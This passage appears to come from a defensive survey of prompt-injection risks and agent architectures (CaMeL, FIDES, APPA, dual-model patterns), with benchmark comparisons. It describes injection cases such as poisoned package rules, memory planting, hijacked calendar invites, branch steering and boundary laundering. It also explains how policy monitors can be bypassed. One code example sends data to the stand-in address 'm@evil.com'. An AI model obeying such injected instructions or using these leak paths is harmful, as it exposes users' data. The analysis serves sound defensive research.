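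Pinning works less well for tools that run on someone else's server. An unchanged description does not prove that the code behind it is unchanged, or that its results are safe to read. Anthropic points out that an owner can inspect a local tool and fix its version, but a remote tool's behaviour can change at any time after approval. Anthropic suggests trying unfamiliar remote tools on fake data first, but a tool that passes the trial can still change later. A closed agent should therefore use only tools that its owner runs, and those tools should return only data that meets the same condition.

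### Package documentation

Programmers want agents to read current documentation, because a model's training data may describe an older version of a package. Context7 supplies such documentation to coding agents. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *ContextCrush Flaw Exposes AI Development Tools to Attacks*, anyone with a GitHub account could register a package there and fill in a field for custom rules. Context7 delivered those rules to agents exactly as submitted, so an attacker could enter malicious rules and wait for a developer's agent to look up the package.

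An attacker could steal credentials from the developer's files or delete files on the developer's machine, according to *CVE-2026-75130 Detail* in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD). The developer's request was routine, and the service was not malicious.

An owner can close this route by keeping a local copy of the documentation for the exact versions in use, having someone read it, and blocking the agent from fetching any other. This is feasible for a handful of packages, but few teams will do the reading for a project that depends on hundreds.

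### Saved memory

If an agent saves notes for later sessions, an attacker needs to reach it only once. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes an early example, which Rehberger published in 2024. In May of that year, he reported to OpenAI that a web page could plant false memories in ChatGPT. OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security concern. In June, he demonstrated that a planted memory could make the macOS app leak later conversations.

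OpenAI's fix in September stopped the app from sending data out through images, but web pages could still write to ChatGPT's memory. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes a later attack that exploited the same weakness. Instructions in a shared file entered the memory, and from then on ChatGPT leaked data before it answered each question.

Companies have also tried to plant memories in AI assistants to promote themselves. Microsoft (2026) examined links in 60 days of email traffic and found 50 different prompts from 31 companies that were meant to influence what an assistant remembers. Many were behind a "Summarize with AI" button, which opened the user's assistant with the prompt already filled in. It asked for a summary and told the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source. All 31 companies were real businesses, and one sold security products. Microsoft counted attempts, and notes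 that the success of such prompts varied between assistants and over time.

Both Microsoft and Embrace The Red advise users to review their saved memories and delete suspicious ones. This review helps only after a memory has been saved, and only if the memory looks suspicious. For a closed agent, it is better to switch memory off or let only the owner write to it. The owner also has to consider other material that an agent reloads in each session, which Anthropic lists as including standing instruction files, shared work folders and the saved state of scheduled agents. Restoring all of these from a reviewed copy before each session removes anything an earlier session left behind.

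### What a signature proves

Reading everything is slow, so owners look for ways to trust a source once and accept whatever comes from it. One option is to accept files that carry the source's digital signature. A valid signature shows that the holder of a certain key approved the file and that nobody has altered it since, but the file could still be harmful.

An attack in May 2026 on TanStack, a widely used family of JavaScript packages, showed the difference. VentureBeat reported that a worm published 84 malicious versions of 42 packages within six minutes, each with a valid attestation, a signed record of the system that built it. According to GitLab, the attacker exploited a misconfigured workflow, tampered with a cache (as in the attack Khan devised against Cline) and took a publishing token from the build machine's memory. TanStack's own release system then produced the malicious packages,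 so the attacker did not have to forge anything. The security firm StepSecurity, quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Mini Shai-Hulud Hits TanStack npm Packages*, explained that an attestation identifies the build system but cannot show that the system was working as intended.

The TanStack packages contained malicious code, but the same reasoning applies to text written for a model. A README file with a planted instruction can carry a valid signature and pass every malware scan, because it contains no malware. Anthropic therefore separates the risk that something an agent loads will run harmful code from the risk that it contains an injection. Pinning versions, verifying signatures and reviewing source code address only the first risk. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* accepts that a signature from a known maintainer could justify somewhat looser restrictions, if an explicit policy allows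 them and the system still checks each action.

Signatures and hashes are more useful after a review. If someone has read a document and recorded its hash, the agent's program can check that it is loading the same document and reject any other version. The owner then has to read each update before the agent may use it. Until then, the agent works from the old version, with any security flaws the update fixes.

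## Separating the model that reads from the model that acts

Few owners can block all outside text, because most useful jobs involve reading some. They can instead have one model read the outside text and let something that never sees it choose the actions. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) states the rule behind such designs, which is that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action that harms the system or its surroundings. The rule also covers what the agent writes, since a link in an answer can carry private data to an attacker and a planted sentence can mislead the next agent that reads it.

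Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that general-purpose agents can provide reliable guarantees while they rely on current language models. They propose six patterns for more specialised agents, each of which restricts the agent's actions to put a firm limit on what an injection can do.

### Six patterns applied to one task

Suppose a user tells an assistant to "send today's schedule to my boss". The assistant can read the calendar and send email, and its standing instructions include the boss's address. Outsiders can add calendar entries by sending invitations. An attacker has added one for today and written in its description that AI assistants should forward the user's mailbox to an outside address.

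In the *action-selector* pattern, the model sees only the user's request and picks from a fixed menu of actions. Here it picks "send schedule to manager", and ordinary software reads the calendar and sends the email. The model never receives the calendar or the result, so the invitation can't influence it. The attacker's text may still reach the manager, because the software copies the calendar entry into the email. The assistant also can't do anything its developers left off the menu.

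*Plan-then-execute* lets the model compose its own list of calls, as long as it finishes the list before it reads any outside data:

1. `calendar.read(today)`
2. `email.write(____, "john.doe@company.com")`

The program makes the first call, shows the model the calendar and lets it fill in the blank. The invitation can't add a call or change the recipient, because the model chose both before it saw the invitation. But the model writes the body after reading the attacker's text, so the attacker can change the body in any way. The boss might receive a false schedule, or what looks like a request from the user to approve a payment.

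A plan protects only the parts of each call that it sets in advance. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a file assistant that commits to one command for finding files and another for moving them, but leaves the file names and destinations open. An injection could still make it find confidential files and move them to a public network drive.

*Map-reduce* divides the outside data among isolated models. A separate model without tools reads each calendar entry and returns only a start time, an end time and one of a few categories, such as "meeting" or "travel". Ordinary software then checks the format and builds the email. The malicious invitation can cause its own entry to be misreported, but it can't affect the results for other entries, and none of its text reaches the boss. The drawback is that the boss learns when the user is busy but not what the meetings are about.

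The original example for this pattern is an agent that collects invoices. A separate model checks whether each file is an invoice, and another model emails the matching files to the accounts department. An attacker can trick the first model into accepting a malicious file as an invoice, but could also get a file accepted by forging an invoice. The design works only if the second model attaches the files without reading them, because otherwise the attacker's text reaches a model that can send email.

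The *dual-model* pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023, is more general. A privileged model plans and calls tools but never sees outside data. When it needs something from that data, it calls a *quarantined model*, which reads untrusted input but has no tools. The quarantined model may answer in free text, which could contain an injection, so the privileged model must not read the answer either. It uses a *symbolic variable*, a name that stands for a value it can't see:

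1. The privileged model asks for today's calendar. The orchestrator, a piece of ordinary software, fetches the entries and stores them under the name `$CAL`.
2. The privileged model asks for a readable version of `$CAL`. The orchestrator gives the entries to the quarantined model and stores its answer as `$VAR`.
3. The privileged model calls `email.write($VAR, "john.doe@company.com")`.
4. The orchestrator replaces `$VAR` with the stored text and sends the email.

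The privileged model receives only the characters `$VAR`, whatever the invitation contains. The attacker can still corrupt the body, but a variable in the recipient field would be more dangerous. If the user asks the assistant to find the boss's address in an old email, the quarantined model supplies the address, and whoever wrote the email may be able to choose it. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) describes such a case. The program had fixed the subject and body, so the injection could not change them, but the recipient came from the email's text and remained untrusted.

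*Code-then-execute* replaces the list of calls with a program, which a model writes before any outside data arrives:

```
schedule = calendar.read(today)
text = quarantined_model("make this readable", schedule)
email.write(text, "john.doe@company.com")
```

A program can contain loops and conditions, so it can handle tasks such as emailing everyone who has a meeting with the user today. In the schedule task, as with the dual-model pattern, the attacker can corrupt the body of the email but can't change who receives it.

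These five patterns don't rule out an injection in the user's own request, for instance one copied from a website. *Context minimisation* reduces this risk by deleting the request once the model has turned it into a calendar query and a recipient. The model that writes the email then receives the query's result but not the request, so hidden text in the request can't make it add a malicious link. That text can still distort the query or the choice of recipient. The calendar entries also still enter the context, so an owner worried about injections in invitations has to combine this pattern with another.

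### How much a restricted answer can carry

Map-reduce works because each isolated model can return very little information. An answer chosen from *k* options carries at most log₂ *k* bits, so a yes/no answer carries at most one bit and a choice among eight categories carries at most three. *n* such answers carry at most *n* log₂ *k* bits, so yes/no answers on 100 files carry at most 100 bits.

An attacker who wrote all 100 files can corrupt all 100 bits, and so choose any of the 2^100 possible sets of files that the agent sends to accounts. An attacker who wrote only one file controls only that file's one-bit answer, because a separate model reads each file. If a single model read all the files together, one malicious file could corrupt all 100 answers.

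Limiting the size of an answer prevents it from containing an instruction, such as one to open a mailbox. A wrong answer can still cause harm, since a single wrong "yes" is enough to approve a fraudulent invoice.

Longer answers leave more room for injected instructions. For coding agents, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a quarantined model convert an outside package's documentation into a formal description of its functions, with names of at most 30 characters. If a name may contain letters, digits and underscores, each character has 63 options, and a full-length name can carry 30 × log₂ 63, or about 179 bits. An instruction such as `run_setup_script_before_use` would fit. The length limit therefore doesn't rule out an injection, although they plausibly argue that one is unlikely to survive sufficiently strict formatting.

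### CaMeL

CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning), a Google DeepMind design from 2025, combines code-then-execute with a check on every tool call. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe its parts, which work together as follows:

1. A privileged model receives the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls.
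3. When the program needs something from untrusted text, the interpreter gives the text to a quarantined model, which extracts the information in a set format, such as an email address. The interpreter stores the answer in a variable.
4. The interpreter tags each value with its sources and with the people who may read it, and keeps track of which values depend on which others.
5. Before each tool call, a policy function written by a developer examines the tool, the values and their tags, and allows or refuses the call.

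The policy check guards against corrupted values in permitted calls. In an example from Nikolaou and colleagues, the program reads a chat channel, asks the quarantined model for Bob's email address and sends Bob the message "Meeting at 3pm". Without policies, an attacker could receive the message by posting a false address in the channel. A CaMeL policy can refuse any recipient whose address came from the channel, but it would then refuse Bob's real address too.

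For the schedule task, a policy could require that the recipient come from a trusted source and have the right to read everything in the body. The boss would meet both conditions. The policy cannot check whether the schedule is accurate, so the attacker could still falsify it.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) uses machine-checked proofs to examine what tags add to the dual-model pattern. In one example, the program reads the user's private notes and a stranger's email, asks the quarantined model for a reply based on both, and sends it to the stranger. Without tags, an injection can make the quarantined model quote the notes. With CaMeL-style tags, the reply counts as private because the notes were among the model's inputs, so the system refuses to send it. This prevents any injection from leaking the notes through the reply, but it also blocks replies that contain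 nothing from the notes.

Tags on values can miss information that leaks through the program's choices. In another of Dongol's examples, the program sends the stranger a 1 or a 0, depending on the quarantined model's answer. Both are harmless constants, so the calls pass the check. But an injection can make the answer depend on the notes, and the stranger then learns one bit about them. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, list other program behaviors that can leak information, such as how many times a loop runs, whether an error occurs and how long a step takes.

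CaMeL has a strict mode meant to track such dependencies, but *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) reports that it has gaps in practice. It cites a finding from *The LLMbda Calculus* that the interpreter can leave a variable marked as trusted when its value depends on an untrusted condition.

CaMeL also assumes that the user's request can be trusted. If the phished employee in Anthropic's exercise had pasted the attacker's prompt into a CaMeL agent, the privileged model would have received the instruction to send out the cloud credentials as part of the task. Only a policy on that data flow could have stopped the transfer. Tallam and Miller propose screening requests for suspicious links and phrases, but this defence is probabilistic and would probably have missed a prompt that looked like routine set-up work.

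The policies take effort to write and maintain. Tallam and Miller point out that every tool needs its own function, so a firm with hundreds of tools can end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules. Each function also examines only one call at a time, so CaMeL can't naturally express rules about a whole run. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security team's agent that must resolve or escalate every incident ticket before it finishes. Their extension, CaMeLoT, maps the paths a program could take and checks such rules before any tool runs. CaMeL might run a long investigation and then refuse the last step for lack of an approval, whereas CaMeLoT can reject the program at the start and ask for a better one.

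### AgentDojo and the cost in completed tasks

Researchers often test these designs on AgentDojo, the benchmark that Alhindi used for seL4. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) simulates four settings: an office workspace, a Slack team, a travel agency and a bank. It includes 97 ordinary tasks, such as paying a bill, and 27 attacker goals, such as obtaining a security code from the user's email. Pairing every task with every goal in the same setting gives 629 test cases. The version that Peters-Gill and colleagues adapted in 2026 has 35 goals and 949 cases.

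In each case, the benchmark plants the attacker's instruction where an outsider's text would normally appear, such as the body of an email. After the run, fixed checks examine the agent's answer and the simulated mailbox, calendar or bank account. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection might fool the judge too. The benchmark reports three rates:

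- how often the agent completes its task when nobody attacks
- how often it completes the task under attack, without harmful side effects
- how often the attacker's goal succeeds.

*Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) also runs each attacker goal as an ordinary task to check whether the agent could achieve it at all. Otherwise, an agent too weak to carry out the attacker's instructions would look secure.

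AgentDojo's standard attacks have become too easy to resist. GPT-5.5 had no failures in the 949 cases that Peters-Gill and colleagues ran without CaMeL, so zero failures on these attacks no longer shows that a design is secure. The benchmark is now more useful for measuring how many tasks a design prevents the agent from completing.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) compares CaMeL with its own system, ELBA, on the 21 Slack tasks. ELBA lets an agent write more code after it has read data and restricts that code according to where the data came from. The table shows how many tasks each system completed when there was no attack.

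| Model | CaMeL, no policies | CaMeL, with policies | ELBA, no policies | ELBA, with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 15 | 5 | 18 | 10 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 6 | 16 | 9 |
| GPT 5.4 | 17 | 5 | 16 | 10 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 13 | 4 | 14 | 8 |

Most of CaMeL's loss here comes from the policies, which make it fail between 9 and 12 of the 21 tasks. This may be because the policies also block actions the user requested. In one Slack task, the user asks the agent to invite Dora to the team, using the email address on her website. A policy that refuses addresses from untrusted pages has to refuse this invitation. The sample is small. Looser policies would have blocked fewer tasks but permitted more attacks.

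Because the standard attacks were weak, Zhou and colleagues also altered ELBA so that any subagent that read a planted instruction received it as its whole task, as if the injection had fully succeeded. The attacker's goal succeeded in 16% to 42% of cases without policies, depending on the model, and in none of the 735 cases per model with them. Task completion was 67% to 76% without policies and 40% to 48% with them. Since the test assumes that the model obeys the attacker, its results show what the rest of the system can prevent.

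Planning ahead can itself reduce an agent's success rate. To measure this effect, Peters-Gill and colleagues ran CaMeL without policies on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks for teams of agents. The success rate fell by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Many failures occurred because the need for another step became clear only after a tool had returned its result. In others, an agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for similar ones. The program had no step for checking this, so it continued with the wrong data.

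### Agents that browse the web or operate a screen

Planning is easier in AgentDojo because its tools have fixed meanings. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (2026) points out that a command to send an email always sends an email, while a click at the same point on a screen might open a product page, submit a purchase or delete an item.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a desktop computer. The privileged model can't see the screen, so it writes a program with a branch for each situation it expects. A quarantined vision model answers questions such as whether a cookie notice is visible and finds the buttons to click. These programs averaged 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 calls and 4 branches for AgentDojo. On OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks, the system kept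 at most 57% of the performance of frontier models.

An attacker can't add steps to such a program but may be able to influence which branch it takes, which Foerster and colleagues call *branch steering*. Most browsing programs include a step for dismissing cookie notices, so the researchers put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. When the program queried the vision model for the notice's location, the model could return the location of the fake one. The click then led to the attacker's site, even though the program had made only calls that its author intended. Foerster and colleagues tried checking the vision model's answers against the page's code and against a second model. They designed an attack to exploit the weaknesses of each check, and they regard any such check as probabilistic.

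*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) describes a later defence that limits every branch to a set of destinations and tools assigned before the program runs. If the task requires a security-critical value that neither the user nor an authorised source has supplied, the system asks the user for it.

Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, avoid ambiguous clicks by having the agent use functions instead. For each website in their tests, they built a documented list of functions by hand, such as one for adding a product to a basket. Their agent, Baya, writes a program from these functions and tests it on simulated data. A separate engine then runs the program on the live site. If the program fails, the model that repairs it receives only limited error information, because a full error message could contain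 an attacker's text.

| Agent | Tasks completed (WebArena Verified) | Attacks that succeed (WASP) | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Baya | 77.8% | 0% | 327 seconds |
| Ordinary agent with browser and website functions | 66.7% | 16.2% | 87 seconds |
| Ordinary agent with browser only | 55.1% | 25.5% | 60 seconds |

Baya completed more tasks than the less secure agents, so separation doesn't always make an agent less capable. But it took almost four times as long as the ordinary agent with website functions, and someone has to prepare every website in advance. That preparation is reasonable for a firm whose agent uses the same five sites every day, but not for an agent that browses freely. Chow and colleagues also don't try to prevent corrupted results. A dishonest seller could still use a product description to make the agent buy a counterfeit, because buying a product is part of the program.

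### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

Suppose the user of the schedule assistant asks it to find the latest email from the boss and do whatever it says. No model can write that program in advance, because the steps are in the boss's email. Chow and colleagues accept that their approach can't support such tasks. They cite an earlier analysis that found no such tasks in WebArena, the benchmark from which their own test set derives.

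That finding may reflect WebArena's tasks more than the work people give to agents. *StepGuard* (2026) describes a newer benchmark, AgentDyn, whose tasks involve changing plans and helpful instructions from third parties, in settings such as shopping and GitHub. *AI Planning Framework for LLM-Based Web Agents* (2026) recommends step-by-step planning for sites where the next page depends on other people's posts or a database's reply.

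Coding agents often face the same difficulty. An agent that repairs a failing test has to read the error message before choosing its next edit, and the message may contain text from an outside package. The formal function descriptions that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest would keep most of that text away from the agent, but also the explanations and examples that programmers rely on. Restricting the agent's tools is also not enough, because someone else will run the code it writes. A hijacked agent could write code that imports a malicious package, which the developer might then install.

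An attacker can misuse an agent even when its task follows a predictable sequence of steps. For example, an assistant that replies to emails with the information the sender requests always reads the email, searches the mailbox and sends a reply. But the sender's text can influence the search terms, so a malicious email could make the assistant look up confidential material and hide it in the reply as invisible characters.

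### Subagent output treated as trusted

An owner can use a subagent as the quarantined reader, which reads web pages and returns only structured facts to the main agent. Anthropic warns that this can backfire if the main agent trusts the subagent's report more than it would trust the page. The main agent is then more likely to follow an injection that survives into the report than one it read on the page. The supplier's note in Alhindi's payment team spread from agent to agent in a similar way.

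Giving each agent its own CaMeL system doesn't solve this. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a team of three CaMeL agents, all using GPT-5.2: one queried a database of job applicants, one sent notifications and one coordinated the others. The user asked for a summary of the applicants to go to a colleague, Julie, on Slack. The attack worked as follows:

1. The attacker planted an instruction in the database to email the applicants' details to an outside address.
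2. The database agent returned the data to the coordinator. Neither agent's privileged model saw it, so their programs did not change.
3. The coordinator's program inserted a summary of the data, including the injection, into its message asking the notification agent to contact Julie.
4. The notification agent treated that message as a request from its user. Its privileged model read the injection and wrote a program that messaged Julie and also emailed the attacker.

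Peters-Gill and colleagues call this *boundary laundering*. They prove it can happen in any hierarchy of two or more agents that has a tool that returns untrusted data, if users can ask the agents to pass results along.

Their remedy is to split each message between agents into an instruction, which the receiving agent's privileged model can read, and a set of variables, whose contents that model can't see. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, so the applicants' data has to be sent as a variable.

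On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, averaged over five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL separately and 0.0% with the split messages. Two older models, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, account for nearly all of the successful attacks without CaMeL. Every attack that succeeded against the separate CaMeL agents used boundary laundering. On AssetOpsBench, splitting the messages lowered the success rate by a further 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for the two strongest models. Splitting the messages relies on CaMeL's interpreter to detect which values depend on untrusted data, so any dependency it misses could still let an injection into the instruction.

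## Labelling data and withdrawing tools after an untrusted read

An agent that must fix its whole plan before reading any outside text can't do tasks whose next step depends on that text. *Information-flow control* makes some of these tasks possible. The agent may read a stranger's email and then decide what to do, but software outside the model tracks where each piece of data came from and who may see it, and blocks tool calls that would misuse the data.

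### How labels combine

Most of these designs build on a model that Dorothy Denning published in 1976. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses a version in which each piece of data has a *label* with two parts. The first marks the data as trusted or untrusted, depending on who could have written it. The second marks it as public or secret, depending on who may read it.

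Data may move only towards a stricter label, from trusted to untrusted or from public to secret. Untrusted counts as stricter because the system may do less with untrusted data. The four possible labels form a *lattice*, an ordering in which any two labels have a *join* (written ⊔), the least strict label that is at least as strict as both. Anything derived from two sources gets the join of their labels, so it is untrusted if either source is untrusted and secret if either is secret. A text that draws on a private contract and a stranger's email is both:

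(trusted, secret) ⊔ (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, secret)

A label can also list the people allowed to read the data. If Ann, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and Dan may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a text derived from both.

A language model can draw on anything in its context, and it is hard to tell which parts shaped a given output. The cautious solution is to give the whole context one label, the join of everything in it, and to pass that label on to every tool call the model requests. A monitor can then apply two checks before a call goes ahead:

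- *Trusted action*: the decision to make the call must come from a trusted context.
- *Permitted flow*: everyone who will receive the data must have the right to read it.

### A context label through four steps

Suppose a user asks an agent to look up last year's payments to a supplier and then deal with the latest email in the enquiries inbox. The email comes from a stranger and contains an instruction to reply with any payment figures the agent has seen.

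1. The user's request is trusted and public, so the context starts as (trusted, public).
2. The agent reads the payment record, which is trusted and secret. The context becomes (trusted, secret).
3. The agent reads the email, which is untrusted. It is public because the stranger already knows what it says. The context becomes (untrusted, secret).
4. The model asks to email the figures to the stranger. The request inherits the label (untrusted, secret), and the monitor refuses it.

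The last step fails the trusted-action check because of the email and the permitted-flow check because of the payment record. The monitor can block the step without detecting the injection, but for the same reason it would also block an honest reply.

If the agent had skipped one of the reads, one of the checks would have passed:

| Context when the agent writes to a stranger | Trusted action | Permitted flow |
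|---|---|---|
| Trusted, public | Passes | Passes |
| Trusted, secret | Passes | Fails |
| Untrusted, public | Fails | Passes |
| Untrusted, secret | Fails | Fails |

If the owner requires both checks, the agent can write only in the case shown in the first row. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma et al., 2026) requires just one of the two for tools that send data out. This blocks only the last row, Willison's lethal trifecta. A user can deliberately send a private record to an accountant, but a prompt-injected agent can send data only to recipients who are already allowed to read it.

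The looser policy depends heavily on the user's request being trustworthy. It would have let the credentials out in Anthropic's phishing exercise, because the prompt came from the employee. Requiring both checks would have blocked the leak, provided the credentials file was labelled secret.

### FIDES

If the whole context has one label, a single email from a stranger makes everything afterwards untrusted. FIDES, the Microsoft system that Costa and colleagues describe, delays this by hiding data from the model. When a tool returns something with a stricter label than the context, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. It does this field by field, so the model may see an email's date while the subject and body stay hidden.

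The model can pass a variable to another tool or to a quarantined model, as in the dual-model pattern. Unlike CaMeL's planner, it can also read the variable's contents. The context then takes on the stricter label, and the model can no longer use tools that require a trusted context.

FIDES also has a compromise between hiding a text and reading all of it, which is to limit the form of the answer. Suppose the user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar:

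1. The agent fetches the emails, and FIDES stores them in a variable.
2. The model asks the quarantined model whether they contain a meeting request. The answer can only be true or false.
3. The model opens the answer. Its label records that it is untrusted but also that it is a single true-or-false value. A policy may accept such a value because it gives an attacker at most one bit of influence.
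4. If the answer is true, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants into another variable.
5. The model passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading it.

An attacker can still put a false meeting in the calendar, but can't make the agent do anything else.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo in 2025, with models that are now old. Without policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic planner using GPT-4o, and 21 succeeded against FIDES. With suitable policies, none succeeded against either. AgentDojo counted three attacks against FIDES as successful, but the researchers reviewed them by hand and found no real injection. The table shows how many tasks each design completed with GPT-4o without any attacks.

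| Design | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic planner, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic planner, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

With checks on, FIDES completed on average 8% more of the tasks than the basic planner with GPT-4o, and 16% more with OpenAI's o1, which made better use of the variables. It did worse on travel tasks because the policies already allowed many travel tools in an untrusted context, so hiding data only made the work harder. Many of the banking failures were intended, because those tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which is the same behaviour an injection relies on.

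The perfect security score depends on the labels. AgentDojo doesn't supply any, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if one of the benchmark's attacks used it. In a real deployment, the owner doesn't know in advance where attackers will write. If an attacker can write to a field the owner marked as trusted, an injection there passes the trusted-action check.

FIDES also tracks only data that moves directly from one place to another, so an observer may still learn something from which tools the agent calls, as with the 1 or 0 in Dongol's CaMeL example. Costa and colleagues accept this gap because closing it would require forbidding almost every public action after the agent has read a secret.

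### Label spread and controlled exceptions

A context label can only become stricter as the agent reads more data. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) proves that with *n* possible readers and *t* levels of trust, the label can tighten at most *n* + *t* − 1 times. By then the agent may be unable to send anything to anyone, so an agent that works for hours across many sources needs exceptions. Something other than the model must grant them, because an injection could manipulate the model.

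Kolluri and colleagues built Prudentia, an extension of FIDES that tells the model about the labels and policies so that it can plan around them. Before opening a hidden text, the model can ask the user to *endorse* it, which changes its label from untrusted to trusted. If an email contains ten tasks, one endorsement replaces ten separate approvals. The user also loses those ten chances to notice a problem, because an instruction hidden among the tasks becomes trusted with the rest. Prudentia has no equivalent for making secret data public, since whether that is appropriate usually depends on the particular tool call.

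On AgentDojo with o3-mini, Prudentia completed 59.1% of tasks without asking anyone, compared with 50.1% for FIDES. With o4-mini and approvals allowed, the completion rates were similar (73.2% for Prudentia and 75.7% for FIDES), but Prudentia needed about 19 interventions over all the tasks it completed, while FIDES needed 37. Kolluri and colleagues assume that people approve and refuse correctly, so the intervention counts measure how often the agent interrupts its user, not how well the user decides.

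APPA, the system that Kravchenko and colleagues propose, uses narrower exceptions. When the monitor blocks a call, it lists the registered ways to proceed. One is a ruling from an outside authority, which may be a fixed rule, a person or a second model. The ruling covers one exact call and leaves the context label unchanged, so the agent can't reuse the ruling for other calls.

Another is to do the reading in a disposable child branch. Suppose a support agent needs three facts from a public issue page:

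1. The agent starts a copy of itself and fixes the form of the answer, for example a ticket number, a severity level and a component name from a list.
2. The copy inherits the parent's label. If it started with a clean label, the agent could use it to launder secrets it had already read.
3. The copy reads the page, and only its own label tightens.
4. The monitor checks the form of the answer, passes it to the parent and discards the rest of the copy's context.

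A hijacked copy can still return a false severity level, and checking the answer's form doesn't show whether it is true. The owner therefore has to decide whether the parent may treat the answer as trusted. Discarding the copy also doesn't undo anything it did with its tools.

APPA checks labels before and after each call. The check before a call covers the data the call will bring in, which matters for tools that read and send in one step. If a tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outsider, a monitor that checks only the current label allows the call because nothing secret has been read yet.

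Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA with GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek V4 Flash and Gemini 3.7 Flash. No attack succeeded in 1,320 runs. On Bench-Corp, a set of 20 corporate workflows, APPA completed 87% to 91% of tasks. Two configurations of FIDES completed 36% to 46% of tasks and failed to stop 26% to 35% of attacks. The comparison is not a fair ranking, because the researchers wrote the FIDES policies themselves and left out several of the rules that Bench-Corp tests, such as exact recipients and the order of steps. On another benchmark, one of the FIDES configurations completed more tasks than APPA with DeepSeek.

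With Luna, removing child branches from APPA reduced completion on Bench-Corp to 56.5%, and removing the list of ways to proceed reduced it to 35.0%. No attacks succeeded in either case. Blocking alone kept the agent secure, but most of the agent's usefulness came from the exceptions.

Zhou and colleagues' system, ELBA, also isolates reading in subagents, but lets them keep using tools within the limits of their labels. Its policy resembles David C's rule of thumb that when a model reads untrusted data, its privileges drop to those of the data's source. With policies on and no attack, ELBA completed about twice as many of AgentDojo's Slack tasks as CaMeL. Under the benchmark's simplest attack, ELBA completed 43 to 52 of 105 tasks and CaMeL completed 23 to 30. ELBA took about three times as long, mainly because the model writes new code after each read.

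### Gaps in the tracking

These systems rely on software to give every value the right label, and mistakes in that software are easy to make. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, show how CaMeL's interpreter can miss a dependency. The following program illustrates the problem:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
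if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is above the threshold. The third line sets `tmp` to false and marks it as secret, because the decision depended on the balance. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so the interpreter never marks `rich` as secret. `rich` is still true and counts as public, so the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out, so the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold.

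CaMeL's retry loop leaks information in another way. When a policy blocks a program, ordinary code outside the interpreter requests a new attempt. If the policy's decision depends on a secret, the presence or absence of a retry reveals one bit of it, and repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret.

Garby and colleagues respond with LLMbda, a small programming language for agents whose interpreter tracks labels through everything, including retries. They prove a form of *noninterference*, meaning a result can depend only on inputs whose labels permit it, except that a secret may affect whether the program finishes. A program can endorse untrusted data only through an explicit command, which an auditor can find. The researchers also prove that endorsing data this way can't make secrets public.

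The Randori agent tests its code on simulated data until it works and only then runs it on the real account, so its retries never depend on real secrets. The table compares Randori with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks.

| Tasks completed | GPT-5.2, no attack | GPT-5.2, under attack | MiMo-v2.5, no attack | MiMo-v2.5, under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Randori, with policies | 75.0% | 65.0% | 64.6% | 59.5% |
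| CaMeL, no policies | 66.7% | 71.1% | 70.8% | 72.2% |
| CaMeL, with policies | 37.5% | 30.0% | 37.5% | 41.5% |

Across three models, Randori resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. Part of its lead in completed tasks may come from enforcing only a subset of CaMeL's policies. Randori also lets its model write endorsements into its own code before the model sees any outside data. When Garby and colleagues removed that option, task completion without attacks fell by about 10 points with MiMo-v2.5 and 12 with Qwen3.7-plus.

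### The reference agent

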